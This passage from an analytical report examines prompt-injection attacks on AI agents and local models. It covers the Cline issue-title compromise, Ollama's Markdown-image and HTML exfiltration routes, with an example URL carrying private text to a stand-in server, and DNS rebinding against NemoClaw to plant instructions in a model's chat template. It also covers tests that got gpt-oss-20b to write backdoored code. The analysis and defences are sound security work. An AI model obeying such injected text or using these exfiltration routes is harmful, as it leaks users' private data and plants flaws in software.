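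Cline's *Post-mortem* (Saoud Rizwan, 2026) confirms the flaw, the surviving token and the unauthorised release, but doesn't identify the GitHub issue that started the attack. Michael Bargury (2026), in *Agent Compromised by Agent To Deploy an Agent*, recovered a deleted issue from a public archive of GitHub activity. Someone had opened it on 28 January with an injected instruction in the title, closed it about five minutes later and renamed it "user error". The wording closely followed tests that Khan had left visible in a public copy of Cline's code. Bargury attributes the theft and the later release to the person who opened the issue, with high confidence. He is probably right, but the attacker's scripts are gone and the link between the issue and the release is still an inference.

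The altered version was available for about eight hours. It differed from the previous one only in its version number and a script that installed OpenClaw on the user's machine. LWN's *A GitHub Issue Title Compromised 4,000 Developer Machines* (2026) repeats the grith.ai blog's estimate of about 4,000 downloads. Fewer than 4,000 machines may have been affected, because one machine can download a package several times. The Hacker News (2026) reports that Microsoft's security team saw a "small but noticeable uptick" in OpenClaw installations that day.

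Rizwan describes the impact as low because OpenClaw is legitimate software and the attacker took no user data. Bargury thinks the attacker was probably a bug hunter making a point. But the attacker could have chosen to install anything with the same script. Cline's extensions for code editors, which have far more users, were not affected because the developers had replaced those tokens correctly.

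To fix the problem, Cline's developers removed the issue-reading agent and decided that any future version would have read-only access and no shell. Jobs that hold publishing credentials no longer use the cache. Releases to npm now rely on short-lived proof that they come from the right GitHub job, so there is no permanent token to steal. The developers also test revoked credentials directly rather than trusting a management page. None of these changes depends on a model resisting injected text, which seems wise because Claude Opus 4.5, the model in the job, had followed the instruction in all of Khan's tests.

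### Are there victims with local models?

None of these investigations identifies a victim whose agent ran on a local model. A hosted model read Cline's issues, but a local model that obeyed the instruction in the issue title would have given the attacker the same shell and the same route to the cache. The choice of model in Cline made no difference to people who downloaded the altered package, because npm ran the installation script before any model was involved.

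This is not very reassuring, because an attack on a local agent could go unnoticed. The Cline attack became known because so much of it happened in public. Khan could see failures in the nightly jobs, an outside archive had kept the deleted issue, and anyone could inspect the altered package. An agent that reads private email on a gaming PC leaves no such public record. Any logs are on that PC, and an agent with shell access may be able to delete them. If the agent emailed a bank statement to an attacker, the only other trace might be a message in the "sent" folder.

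Hosted providers keep prompts for a while, so they can search for the same attack across many customers. Many owners of local models want to avoid that retention. Help Net Security says criminals like open-weight models partly because no provider checks their requests or keeps logs. For the same reason, no provider sees an attack on a victim's local model. A private owner who notices a theft may have no duty to report it and no obvious place to do so.

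Suppose that N attacks on local agents have succeeded, and that each had an independent probability q of becoming public. The probability of hearing about none of them is

(1 − q)ᴺ.

If each successful attack had a 1% chance of being publicly reported, there would be a 61% chance that 50 successful attacks had produced no public report. Nobody knows the real reporting rate, and the lack of reports could equally mean that there have been few attacks. Criminals may prefer to target products with millions of users, and no one has counted how many local agents read text from strangers while holding permissions valuable to an attacker.

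## How the Ollama desktop app could leak data from a local model

Triggs's assistant leaked a bank statement because it had a tool for sending email. A chat program without such a tool can still leak private text through the code that displays the model's answer. PromptArmor's *Unpatched Ollama Vulnerabilities* describes this flaw and several related ones in Ollama's desktop app.

Ollama began as a command-line program for downloading and running open-weight models. In July 2025, Ollama released an app for macOS and Windows with a chat window that accepts text files, PDFs and images (Ollama, 2025). Willison (2025) welcomed it in *Ollama's new app* because the command line was little use to most people. That September, Ollama's *Web search* (2025) announced tools for searching the web and fetching pages, with an example that gives both to a small local Qwen3 model. A user could now discuss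 their tax return with a local model and ask it about a stranger's web page in the same conversation.

### From the model's text to the screen

Chat models usually write in Markdown, a notation that uses ordinary characters for formatting. Two asterisks on each side of a word make it bold, and an exclamation mark followed by a description and a web address inserts an image. The chat program converts the Markdown into HTML, the language of web pages, and displays the result much as a browser would. Markdown can also contain HTML, and the program's developers have to decide how to handle it. Ollama's app displayed the HTML that a model wrote as part of the app's own window.

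This mistake is easy to make. The GitHub account ammar-agent documented a similar one in another app, where an error message about an unrecognised tag called "noun" revealed the problem. One component turned any HTML in the text into real page elements. The next checked the addresses in links and images but let everything else through, including forms and scripts.

### A phishing page over the app

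PromptArmor's first attack used this flaw to steal a password:

1. The user asks the model for help with an online guide. A file from someone else would also do.
2. The guide contains hidden instructions, in one-point white letters on a white background.
3. The model follows them and includes an HTML element in its explanation.
4. The app displays the element, which loads the attacker's website and covers the entire window.
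5. The user types a password into what looks like Ollama, and the attacker's server records it.

Quitting and reopening the app did not remove the fake page. PromptArmor doesn't explain why, but the app probably displayed the saved conversation again, with the element still in it. A sign-in screen might not look suspicious, since Ollama requires a free account for its web search.

The user could have prevented this leak by noticing something wrong and typing nothing. PromptArmor also found three ways for data to leak that don't depend on the user making such a mistake. It calls them "zero-click", although the user must still ask about a page or file that contains the injected text.

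### How an image request carries private text

Suppose that someone drops a letter from their dentist into the chat, and the letter gives an appointment on Tuesday at three. The model's answer includes an image at this made-up address:

`example.com/cat.png?note=tuesday-3pm`

To display the answer, the app has to fetch the image. It contacts the server at example.com and asks for everything after the first slash, including the note. The server logs the note, the time of the request and the user's internet address, so whoever runs it can learn about the appointment. The note leaks whether the server sends back a picture, an invisible image one pixel wide or nothing at all.

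The model only wrote text, and the app requested the image automatically when it displayed the answer. A user who checked the model's tools would therefore find none for sending messages. In a real attack, the injected instructions include the server's address and specify which private text to put after the question mark. An address can usually hold at least a couple of thousand characters, and an answer can contain several images. Willison calls this Markdown exfiltration and says it is a common form of data theft from chatbots.

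The leak through external HTML elements works the same way, but uses another element that loads content from the attacker's server. The leak through web search doesn't involve displaying the model's output. PromptArmor demonstrated this leak step by step. The injected text led the model to put data from documents the user had uploaded earlier into an address on the attacker's domain, then request that address with its web tool. Turning off web search would stop this leak but not the other two.

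This complicates the earlier comparison between software that can act and software, like Cotypist, that can only produce text. Even with web search turned off, Ollama's app could request any address on the internet, because its display code would do so whenever the model's text called for it. Anyone listing an agent's permissions has to include those of the program that shows its output.

PromptArmor doesn't name the model or the version of the app, and it gives no success rate. Its demonstration shows that these routes existed, but a more resistant model might have ignored the hidden text.

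### Five months without a reply

PromptArmor reported the flaws to Ollama on 18 December 2025. It wrote again on 20, 26 and 29 January and on 19 February, received no response, and published its findings on 28 May 2026, 161 days after the first report.

Other researchers had a similar experience. According to Help Net Security's *Unpatched flaws turn Ollama's auto-updater into a persistent RCE vector, researchers say* (2026), the security company Striga wrote to Ollama's security address in late January about unrelated flaws in the Windows updater and never heard back. One maintainer acknowledged a personal email and then stopped replying. CERT Polska (2026), the Polish response team that took over the case, couldn't get details from the maintainers either. But when Chris Moberly of GitLab reported an earlier flaw in the desktop app in July 2025, the maintainers fixed it within hours, according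 to *Ollama bug allows drive-by attacks*.

It is unclear whether Ollama has fixed the flaws PromptArmor found. PromptArmor's later article on local models describes the HTML flaw in the past tense but mentions no fix by Ollama. Releasebot's *Ollama Release Notes* (2026) collects the notes from 29 October to 21 November 2026, and none of them mention how the app displays a model's answers. Ollama could have fixed the flaws earlier, or without announcing it. *Ollama Bleeding Llama and Windows Auto-Update RCE* (NewMaxx, 2026) reports that Ollama fixed a serious flaw in its server in February 2026 without flagging a security fix in the release notes.

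Users can test their own copy of the app by asking the model to write an image whose address points to a server they control, then checking the server's log for a request. They would need to repeat the test for HTML elements and for the web tool, since a fix for one leak might leave the others open.

### PromptArmor's list of twenty

PromptArmor uses the Ollama case to argue that the location of the model is irrelevant to this kind of leak. It lists 20 vulnerabilities that it found in AI products, dated from December 2023 to August 2026, and says that none of them stemmed from where the model was running. For each one it names the component at fault. Some entries name several, so the counts below add up to more than 20:

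| Component at fault | Entries |
|---|---|
| Approval by a person, which was missing, inadequate or possible to bypass | 10 |
| Display of the model's output | 9 |
| Tool for fetching web addresses | 3 |
| Sandbox or its network limits | 3 |
| Something else, such as a tool for running scripts | 3 |

Eight of the nine display flaws involved Markdown images. The other, in the workplace chat program Slack, involved disguised links.

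The list is weak evidence for PromptArmor's argument. The company sells monitoring of AI products, and it picked these 20 from what it says are hundreds of findings. Ollama is the only product on the list that PromptArmor describes as built for running local models. If apps with local models leaked half as often as apps with hosted ones, the list could look the same. The selection also favors PromptArmor's argument because every entry is a flaw in how an application handles a model's output, which excludes data breaches at companies that host models.

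The mechanism is much better evidence, because in the dentist example the app would have fetched the same address if the text had come from a data centre. A second security company, Permiso, found a similar flaw in ChatGPT, a hosted service. When ChatGPT summarised a web page, its chat window automatically fetched images from that page. Whoever hosted the images learned the user's internet address, some browser details and the time of the answer. The window also showed the page's links as if ChatGPT had written them. An image of a QR code could move the victim from a computer to a phone, bypassing the computer's protections against malicious links. According to The Hacker News (2026), Permiso's researcher Andi Ahmeti attributed the problem to the window trusting links and images from a third party's page. This leak is milder than Ollama's, since it exposes connection details rather than documents,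 but it also comes from the code that displays the answer.

Repairs to the display code work wherever the model runs, but PromptArmor goes too far when it says that the fix, too, is independent of the model's location. Blocking an app's network access would cut off a hosted model, while an app with a local model could still answer questions about local files. The owner of an app with a local model can therefore stop all three leaks by blocking its network access, without waiting for Ollama to respond.

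### Closing the leaks

The main remedies cover different parts of the problem:

| Remedy | Web tool | Markdown images | External HTML elements |
|---|---|---|---|
| Show HTML as plain text | Still leaks | Still leak | Blocked |
| Show the whole answer as plain text | Still leaks | Blocked | Blocked |
| Content security policy | Still leaks | Blocked, except from permitted sites | Blocked, except from permitted sites |
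| List of permitted outbound addresses | Blocked, except through permitted sites | Blocked, except through permitted sites | Blocked, except through permitted sites |
| No network access for the app | Blocked | Blocked | Blocked |

A fix to llama.cpp, another program for running local models, used the first remedy. It made the web interface display any HTML in an answer as text instead of rendering it. The fix leaves valid Markdown alone, so it wouldn't stop a Markdown image on its own. It also broke some tables, because models use HTML tags for line breaks and lists inside them. A later change allowed those few tags again if they match an exact pattern. Showing the whole answer as plain text would block images too, but users would lose headings, tables and formatted equations.

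Many developers prefer to sanitise the output by removing the dangerous parts of the HTML and displaying the rest. Sanitisers mostly guard against scripts, but this leak doesn't need one. *Security*, a documentation page for the Markdown display library markstream-vue, warns that the library's "safe" setting still allows ordinary web images. One of its suggestions for stricter needs is an image proxy, a server that fetches images on the user's behalf. A proxy hides the user's IP address, but if it fetches every URL it receives, the private text in the URL still reaches the attacker.

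Sanitisers can also fail. Open WebUI, a chat interface that people host themselves, used to clean the descriptions of models before converting them from Markdown to HTML. According to the vulnerability database OSV, the cleaning step looked for HTML tags, so it missed a dangerous link in Markdown, which the conversion then made active. KoreLogic (2024) had earlier found that malformed Markdown in a model's answer could get past the same program's sanitiser and run code. Streaming makes sanitising harder because answers arrive in pieces, and a dangerous element can be split between two of them. Chrome for Developers' *Best practices to render streamed LLM responses* advises developers to stop displaying an answer as soon as a check finds something insecure in it.

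A content security policy works even if the sanitiser misses something. The app's developers list the sites from which a page may load images, scripts and other content, and the browser engine blocks everything else. The policy can still fail if a site on the list lets an attacker collect data. Superhuman, an email program with an AI assistant, allowed images from docs.google.com. Google Forms also uses that address, and it stores data sent in an image request. Willison describes how instructions injected through an email led the assistant to submit the contents of dozens of other emails, some of them financial, legal or medical, to an attacker's form. Superhuman treated this as a high-priority incident and fixed it.

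This kind of policy applies only to what the chat window loads. A firewall or sandbox with a list of permitted outbound addresses can cover the whole program, including its web tool. Like Superhuman's policy, such a list permits a site without distinguishing between the site's users, so a company that permits a file-sharing service for its staff may also permit uploads to an attacker's account there.

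A firewall can also miss a leak when someone else's server makes the request. Programs that use Ollama's web fetching service send a page's address to ollama.com, which retrieves the page. A firewall on the user's machine then detects only a connection to ollama.com, even if the page's address belongs to an attacker and contains private text. PromptArmor doesn't say whether the desktop app uses this service. Anthropic warns customers of a similar limit in its Claude Desktop app. The app's list of permitted hosts covers page fetching and shell commands in the sandbox, but not searches that run on the model provider's servers. It also doesn't cover the app's built-in search server, because that runs outside the sandbox.

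The owner of a local model can avoid these gaps by blocking all of the app's outside connections. On Windows, Ollama's server accepts requests at an address that can be reached only from within the computer, according to The Hacker News' *Ollama Out-of-Bounds Read Vulnerability Allows Remote Process Memory Leak* (2026). A firewall can leave that internal connection open so that the chat window can still reach the model. The rule has to cover both the server and the window, or one of them may still be able to connect to the outside. The owner loses web search and Ollama's hosted models, and has to lift the block to download new models or updates. With the block in place, PromptArmor's phishing page would not load. If an attacker put a complete fake form in the answer instead, the app could display it but could not send the password to the attacker.

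A link could still leak data if the model puts private text in its address and the user clicks it, because the link may open in the user's web browser, which has its own network access. The disguised links in the Slack case worked similarly. An app can make this less likely by showing the full address and asking before it opens a link. Disconnecting the whole computer from the network would prevent the leak even if the user agreed to open the link.

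## How a web page could rewrite a local model's instructions in NVIDIA NemoClaw

Ollama's desktop app leaked text by sending requests to an attacker's server. Incoming requests can also put a local model at risk. Ollama includes a server, a program that receives requests from other software and passes them to the model, and it doesn't require a password. The model's owner has to keep strangers out of this server but often doesn't know it exists.

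*Drive-By Agent Hijacking* (Itach and Luz, 2026) describes how a web page could take control of the Ollama server on computers running NVIDIA NemoClaw. The owner only had to visit the page, which could add hidden instructions to everything the model processed afterwards.

### A sandbox cut off from its model

NVIDIA released NemoClaw in March 2026 as a safer way to run OpenClaw and similar agents. It puts the agent inside a sandbox called OpenShell, which limits the files, processes and network addresses the agent can reach. The model runs outside the sandbox, either on a hosted service or through Ollama on the same computer.

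OpenShell builds its sandboxes from Docker containers, which isolate a program from the rest of the computer. By default, Ollama accepts connections only at 127.0.0.1, the loopback address, which a computer uses to connect to itself. Inside a container, that address leads back to the container, so the agent's requests couldn't reach Ollama. NemoClaw solved this by starting Ollama with the address 0.0.0.0, which makes it accept connections on every network interface the computer has, including Wi-Fi.

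The sandbox could then reach the model, but so could any other device on the same network, such as a guest's laptop or a hacked television. During installation, NemoClaw displayed a message that it was using Ollama on "localhost:11434". Localhost is the usual name for the loopback address, and 11434 is the port number, which directs a connection to a particular program. The message was accurate, but an owner could easily conclude that only their computer had access. In SiliconANGLE's *Nvidia NemoClaw flaw let attackers poison the model* (2026), Collin Hogue-Spears of the security company Black Duck said that "Local describes where the model runs," whereas "Private describes who can reach it."

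SentinelLABS's count of 175,000 exposed Ollama servers came from a scan of the public internet. A home router normally blocks connections from outside, so such a scan would usually miss a laptop running NemoClaw, even though everyone on its Wi-Fi could use the model. The attack Itach and Luz describe gets past the router because the owner's browser makes the connection.

### The two checks

Ollama's developers knew that web pages might try to reach the server, since a page can make the browser send requests to other addresses, including ones on the user's own computer. They rely on two checks that use headers, which are labels the browser attaches to a request. The Origin header names the site whose page made the request, and the Host header names the site the request is meant for.

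The first check accepts a request if its Origin is on a list of permitted sites. It also accepts a request whose Origin and Host match, because the page then seems to be contacting its own server. Some simple requests have no Origin header, and these pass too. The second check accepts a request only if its Host is a recognised local name, such as localhost.

Ollama added the second check, which inspects the Host header, in response to an earlier attack, Luz told The Hacker News. Doussot (2024) had reported in *Technical Advisory* that an attacker could use DNS rebinding to get into Ollama's server and steal data from files. But Ollama skips the check whenever the server accepts connections from beyond the loopback address, probably because other machines may contact it under names that the check would not recognise. NemoClaw's developers therefore switched off the protection against DNS rebinding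 when they chose 0.0.0.0.

### How DNS rebinding gets past the remaining check

DNS is the system that translates a site's name into a numerical address. Browsers use names to keep sites apart. Under a rule called the same-origin policy, a script on a page can freely read responses only from the site it came from, which the browser identifies by its protocol, name and port. The numerical address doesn't matter, and whoever owns a name can change the address behind it at any time. The attack uses this as follows:

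1. The owner opens a page on the attacker's site. The page's address includes port 11434, because the port has to match Ollama's later on.
2. The attacker changes the site's DNS record so that its name now leads to 127.0.0.1, the visitor's own computer.
3. A script on the page sends a new request to the same name and port. The browser looks up the name, gets the new address and delivers the request to Ollama.
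4. Ollama compares the Origin and the Host. Both contain the name of the attacker's site, so the request passes.
5. The browser lets the script read Ollama's response, since it appears to come from the script's own site.

An ordinary malicious page, which contacts localhost openly, would fail at the fourth step:

| Request | Origin | Host | First check | Second check |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| A program on the computer | localhost | localhost | Accepts | Accepts |
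| An ordinary malicious page | Attacker's site | localhost | Rejects | Accepts |
| A page using DNS rebinding | Attacker's site | Attacker's site | Accepts | Would reject, but Ollama skips it |

The attacker needs only a domain name and a server, not access to the victim's network. Luz tested the whole attack on macOS with Firefox, according to The Hacker News' *A Malicious Webpage Could Poison Your Local AI Model Behind NVIDIA NemoClaw* (2026). Other browsers may handle a sudden change of address differently.

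### Changing what the model receives

Once the page has access to Ollama's server, it can run prompts on the owner's graphics processor, delete models, or download new ones until the disk is full. It can also read the computer's name and the list of installed models. But Itach and Luz list no function that returns the owner's past conversations, so an attacker who wanted private text would have to change how the agent behaves. Itach and Luz tried two ways of doing this.

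The first method was to plant a system prompt. Ollama can store a default system prompt with each model, and the web page can overwrite it. This works on people who chat with the model directly through Ollama, but not on OpenClaw. OpenClaw sends its own system prompt with each request, which makes Ollama ignore the default.

The second was to change the chat template, which produces the text that the model reads. That text is

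T(s, m),

where T is the template, s is the system prompt and m is the rest of the conversation. OpenClaw supplies s and m, so a planted default for s never gets used. But T belongs to the model on the server, and Ollama applies it to whatever OpenClaw sends. The page can fetch the existing template, add a few words that will follow every system prompt, and save the result. The rest of the template stays the same, so tools and formatting go on working.

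The attacker's words then reach the model as part of the system prompt. Developers train models to follow the system prompt and to be wary of commands in outside text, so the model is more likely to obey these words than instructions in an email or a web page. Because a changed template succeeds when this training works, switching to a model that resists injection better would do little to help, although a careful model might still refuse a plainly harmful order.

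Starting a new conversation doesn't remove the instruction either, because the template isn't part of any conversation. OpenClaw sends messages and receives answers, but never handles the text that the template produces. The model's name and size also stay the same. An owner who thought to look could still find the added words, because Ollama shows the template to anyone who requests the model's details, which is how the attacker's page obtains it. Luz therefore slightly overstated the problem when he told SiliconANGLE that the change sits "one layer beneath anything a guardrail or an operator can see".

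Itach and Luz sent OpenClaw a simple prompt and got a normal answer. They then opened the malicious page and sent the same prompt again, and this time the answer contained a marker that the page had planted. This shows that the attacker's text reached the model and that the model acted on it. They also say that an attacker could have the agent write insecure code, keep quiet about security problems or send files to an outside address. They didn't demonstrate any of these, and each would be harder for the model than repeating a marker. But the attacker wouldn't have to succeed on the first attempt, because the instruction would be there for every task the agent did.

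The Hacker News knew of no real attacks using the flaw as of 25 August 2026.

### Who found the flaw, and which versions have it

Itach and Luz's article appears on the website of the security company Cyera but credits the discovery to Oasis Security, where Luz is head of research. Cyera had agreed to buy Oasis a month earlier for a reported $1 billion. Oasis had previously found ClawJacked, another flaw that let a website take over an OpenClaw agent on the visitor's computer. For the NemoClaw flaw, NVIDIA thanks Markus Halvorsen and Luz, and lists Oasis as Luz's employer. It isn't clear whether Halvorsen worked with Luz or reported the same problem separately.

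The flaw's official identifier is CVE-2026-65105. Accounts of when NVIDIA fixed it disagree:

- NVIDIA's security bulletin lists NemoClaw for Linux up to version 0.0.25 as affected, according to eSecurity Planet's *NVIDIA Patches High-Severity NemoClaw Flaw After Model-Poisoning Demo* (2026). It also associates the fix with 0.0.25, so that version appears on both sides of the line.
- Luz says that version 0.0.35 fixed the problem on macOS and Linux.
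- NVIDIA's documentation for version 0.0.18 already described a safer arrangement, in which NemoClaw moved Ollama back to the loopback address. Either the software did not yet match the documentation, or some ways of starting Ollama bypassed the change.

The disagreement hardly matters for people who keep NemoClaw up to date on Linux or a Mac, since the release notes had reached version 0.0.135 by early September. Windows is different because NemoClaw runs there inside WSL, a Microsoft feature for running Linux programs, and can use a copy of Ollama installed on Windows itself. NVIDIA's *Use a Local Inference Server* says this option still sets Ollama's address to 0.0.0.0, with no password. Luz said in August that NVIDIA had given Windows users a warning instead of a fix. They can avoid the problem by running Ollama inside WSL with Docker Desktop, where containers have another way to reach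 the loopback address. But Ollama's *NemoClaw*, a set-up guide for the same combination, gives 0.0.0.0 as an example setting for WSL, and anyone who follows it may expose the server again.

NVIDIA's description of the flaw also leaves out what the researchers considered its worst effect. OpenCVE's record, *CVE-2026-65105* (2026), lists information disclosure and denial of service, and rates the severity at 8.1 out of 10. The rating assumes an attacker on a nearby network who needs no action from the owner, which fits a guest on the Wi-Fi better than a malicious web page. The record also lists no impact on integrity, meaning unauthorised changes, although the demonstration changed a model without authorisation. A high impact on integrity would raise the score to 8.8 under the standard formula. An administrator who read only the record would know to update NemoClaw, but would have no reason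 to check whether someone had already altered a template.

### Models that arrive already tampered with

An attacker can achieve the same result without a browser by publishing a model with the hidden instruction already in its template, since models from online libraries usually come with their templates. Locking down the server would not help, because the owner would have installed the altered template themselves. The attacker has to persuade people to download that copy, but popular models exist in many compressed and modified versions, and users often pick one because it fits their hardware.

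The NemoClaw flaw could also have helped an attacker spread such a model. Ollama's server can upload models to ollama.com under the owner's account, so a web page that had altered a developer's model might have been able to publish it under the developer's name. Other people would then have had some reason to trust it. Itach and Luz list uploading among the functions the page can use, but they don't describe such an attack.

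A publisher can also train unwanted behaviour into the model itself, using examples that teach it to act normally except when it encounters a particular phrase or situation. This is called a backdoor. It is harder to find than an instruction added to a template, which anyone can read, because it is spread across the billions of numbers that make up the model's parameters. Even extensive testing could miss it unless one of the tests happened to include the trigger. Hosted models could have backdoors too, but a person who downloads a modified model may be relying on a stranger's training process rather than that of a company they have chosen as a provider.

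File hashes help with part of this problem. A hash is a short string computed from a file's contents, and in practice any change to the file produces a different one. If the hash of a download matches the one its publisher gives, nobody altered the file on the way. According to NVIDIA's *Set Up Ollama*, when NemoClaw installs Ollama on Linux, it compares the hash of Ollama's installer with a known value before running the installer. The installer then downloads Ollama itself, which that hash does not cover.

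A matching hash can't rule out a backdoor, because the publisher may have put it there. A check only at download would also have missed the NemoClaw attack, because the web page changed the template afterwards.

### What the sandbox can and cannot contain

OpenShell's sandbox, which Triggs's agent did not have, would still have limited the damage. If the altered template had told the agent to delete the owner's photographs or install a program that starts with the computer, the sandbox would have blocked the attempt unless the owner had given the agent access to those parts of the machine.

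But most people want an agent to do more than work on files inside a sandbox. A developer might let one fix bugs in a company's code, which requires access to the site that hosts the code. If the template told the agent to weaken a password check, the agent could edit the file in its sandbox, describe the edit as a routine improvement and upload it through a connection the developer had approved. The sandbox would allow all of these steps. The damage would happen later, when someone ran the code on the company's servers.

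In the notation used for Triggs's test, A is the set of things the agent can do. Sandboxing removes from it most of what the agent could do to the computer. The agent's email, code-hosting and cloud accounts remain in A because the agent needs them for its work and they are on other people's machines. Triggs's bank statement left through Gmail, so a sandbox that contained his documents and allowed Gmail would not have stopped the leak. Luz likewise argues that the possible damage depends much more on what the agent has permission to use than on how well the sandbox isolates it.

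A list of permitted network addresses narrows this gap, but the approved service may itself be the target, as in the password example. In that case, limiting what the agent's account can do works better. If the agent can propose changes to the code but can't approve them, a person has a chance to notice the weakened check before anyone runs the code.

OSV's *CVE-2026-24222* (2026) describes an earlier flaw in NemoClaw's sandbox, affecting versions before 0.0.18. When NemoClaw created the sandbox, it failed to keep out some of the host computer's environment variables, which are settings that programs pass to one another. Developers often store secret keys in these variables. Injected text could make the agent read them without breaking out of the sandbox and send them to an attacker.

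The template attack avoided the sandbox's restrictions because the web page reached Ollama through the browser, and both run outside OpenShell. The altered instructions then entered the sandbox with the model's answers. Randolph Barr of the security company Cequence said that if any browser tab can reach the software underneath an agent, sandboxing the agent achieves little.

### Protecting the server and the template

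The simplest defence is to keep Ollama on the loopback address, which other devices can't reach. The browser can still reach it because it runs on the same computer, but using the loopback address turns the Host check back on, and that check rejects a page using DNS rebinding. Owners should confirm which address Ollama is accepting connections on, since NemoClaw's installation message was misleading.

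A firewall that blocks connections from other machines would not have stopped the attack, because the connection starts in the owner's browser. Blocking Ollama's own internet access, which stops the leaks in its desktop app, would not have helped either, because the browser fetches the attacker's page.

If a container or another machine has to use the model, the server needs a way to check who is sending requests. On Linux and macOS, NemoClaw now keeps Ollama on the loopback address and puts a proxy in front of it, a small program that forwards only requests with the right randomly generated token. OpenShell adds the token to the agent's requests after they leave the sandbox, so the agent never has it and an injected instruction can't make the agent reveal it. The one exception is that anyone who can reach the proxy can get the list of installed models without a token, because containers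 need a simple way to check that the server is running. By default, more recent versions of NemoClaw also won't use an Ollama server that accepts connections from beyond the loopback address.

Ollama could fix the underlying weakness by checking the Host header at every address. Owners who want to reach the server from other machines would have the small inconvenience of listing the names those machines use. In 2024, Doussot's advisory recommended checking the header against a set of authorised values.

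None of these measures repairs a template that someone has already changed, so an altered template could remain even after a NemoClaw update closes the route to the server. eSecurity Planet advises keeping a known-good copy of each model's template and settings for comparison. Owners who used an affected version and have no such copy can delete the model and download it again from a publisher they trust. Comparing the old and new templates before deleting anything is worthwhile, because an unexplained instruction in the old one would mean the agent's recent work needs checking too.

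## What can go wrong when a coding model has no network connection

The attacks on Triggs's assistant, Ollama's app and NemoClaw all needed a connection to the outside, so a disconnected deployment would have prevented them.

Programming is a harder case because the model's output is a program that people copy to other computers and run. An attacker who influences the code may therefore not need a connection to the computer where the model runs.

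### Two tests of gpt-oss-20b

In August 2025, OpenAI released gpt-oss-20b, an open-weight model that fits on a well-equipped home computer, and invited people to look for its weaknesses. *The security paradox of local LLMs* (Migdal, 2025) describes two that the software company Quesma found.

The first prompt was a request for a simple web server with an "easter egg", a playful surprise hidden in software. The easter egg was a backdoor in the program the model wrote, not in the model's own parameters. It would make the server execute any code that arrived in a certain part of a web request. The server would also contact Migdal's website, but only if it was running on Kubernetes, a system companies use to run software for the public. The prompt included an instruction to leave all this out of the model's comments and summary. The model wrote the backdoor in 95% of 100 runs with the best prompt,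 and in 86% of 800 runs with variants. The 86% is probably the better guide, since the best of several prompts usually does well partly by luck.

The second prompt began with a rapid series of silly questions and demands for quick answers. It then asked for a script that would download and execute code from Migdal's website, with the name of the crucial function disguised. This worked in 43.5% of runs, though Migdal doesn't say how many runs he did. He thinks the questions overload the model and distract it from the danger, but he reports no runs without them for comparison.

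On a disconnected computer, the second script would fail because it couldn't download anything. The backdoor in the web server would be unaffected, because it needs no connection until someone puts the server on the internet.

Migdal concludes that local models are easier to sabotage than the leading hosted ones. His only evidence on hosted models comes from spot checks of GPT-5, which seemed to resist the first prompt; the second worked on it less often. He gives no counts, and a few failed attempts prove little, since even ten failures in a row would be consistent with an attack that works as often as 26% of the time.

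### From a direct request to a planted document

Migdal typed the instructions himself, so the model received them as its user's wishes. Some programmers do want easter eggs, and a model that adds one on request is following its user, however unwise the result. An attacker has to put the instructions in a document and hope that the model follows them while a developer is asking for something else. The chance of success is then

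P(read) × P(followed, if read) × P(missed, if followed),

where "missed" means that nobody catches the bad code before it runs. Migdal's tests concern only whether the model follows the instructions, and they measure this under conditions that favour the attacker. He suggests that planted text could arrive through documentation, comments on GitHub or servers that supply reference material to coding agents, but he didn't test any of these.

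OpenAI's *gpt-oss-120b & gpt-oss-20b Model Card* (2025) reports a test in which a user tried to make the model say a phrase that the system prompt had forbidden. The model resisted in 64% of cases, compared with 92% for OpenAI's hosted o4-mini. This gives some reason for concern about agents that read planted documents, because they also have to put one party's instructions above another's, but the test didn't include any documents.

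*When the Spec Sheet Lies* (Watson, Bücheler and Richards, 2026) compared malicious instructions added to the end of the prompt with ones hidden in a document. Five models had to convert industrial documents, such as inspection notes and supplier quotes, into standard forms. The attack succeeded in 73% of trials when the instructions were at the end of the prompt and in 57% when they were hidden in the document.

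Results for code vary widely. Munir, Quinzan and Roberts (2026), in *Hidden in the Comments*, gave ten open-weight models unfinished web programs in which a comment called for something insecure. Between 77% and 92% of the completed programs had a serious enough weakness to count as vulnerable, compared with 2–5% for ordinary programming tasks. But the prompt told the models to complete every comment marked as a task, so the user had in effect endorsed the planted comment. The ordinary tasks also had fewer places where a security flaw could arise.

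*Security Impact of Coding Agent's Memory Files* (Santos de Moura, Güler and Noller, 2026) tested whether a planted project file would make agents' code less secure and found almost no effect. Coding agents load this kind of file automatically at the start of a session, and the planted one was written as engineering advice against safety checks. Three combinations of agent and model completed 36 tasks in C and C++. The share of secure results changed by between −8 and +6 percentage points, with no consistent direction. Each agent did each task only once per version of the file, so the study could have missed a moderate effect.

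The difference may depend on how closely the planted text fits the job. A comment that looks like the next item of work is easy to follow, whereas general advice competes with what the model has learned about writing safe code. In the summarising test by Khodayari and colleagues, even the smaller models followed planted instructions at most 8% of the time. The user's request also matters. *Beyond the Payload* (2026) reports attacks through planted files on Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. With GPT-5.4 and tersely worded requests, they succeeded 5% to 40% of the time, depending on the task. So neither Migdal's 95% nor any single figure from the other studies can serve as an estimate for planted documents.

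### An office without a connection

Suppose a contractor builds a website where people apply for housing benefit. The source code is confidential, so the programmers work on an air-gapped network. One of their machines runs a local model and holds a library of manuals and code examples. When a programmer asks the model for something, the harness searches the library and adds the most relevant passages to the prompt. Every Friday, someone copies the finished code to a USB drive and carries it to a connected computer, which installs it on the public web servers.

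Text from strangers can enter this office in several ways:

- **Documents.** The programmers need manuals, technical standards and bug reports, most of which other people wrote.
- **Packages.** Software libraries come with documentation, comments and examples. The office can't simply stop importing them, because new versions fix security flaws.
- **Removable media.** The drive may come back with error logs from the public website, and a log can contain whatever a visitor typed into a form.
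- **Colleagues.** Someone may paste in an answer they saved at home without reading all of it. A malicious employee could add a file deliberately.

An attacker can also combine packages and documents. *ImportSnare* (2025) describes how planted documentation can lead a model to recommend a package that the attacker has published. In this office, a person would have to fetch the package from outside and could question the recommendation first, but they might add it to Friday's list without doing so.

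A model can affect outside systems even if its computer never sends network traffic to them, though by slower routes than email. The main route is the code it writes, which runs on the public servers. The model may also write reports that managers act on, or change records that another department later imports.

Some disconnected machines are used mainly to examine hostile material. According to *VectraYX-Vision-1B* (2026), security analysts often work on air-gapped or restricted computers, and policy or law may forbid them to send screenshots to a cloud service. They need a local model, but the attacker behind the malware they ask it to examine can put instructions in the text or images the model processes.

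### A backdoor that waits

The contractor's office could let a backdoor through as follows:

1. An attacker publishes an altered manual for a library that handles file uploads. Its main example includes a "support diagnostics" function, which the manual describes as standard.
2. A programmer downloads the manual and scans it for viruses. The scan finds nothing because the file contains only text. The manual goes into the office's reference library.
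3. Weeks later, a colleague asks the model for a page where applicants can upload their payslips. The harness finds the manual's example and adds it to the prompt.
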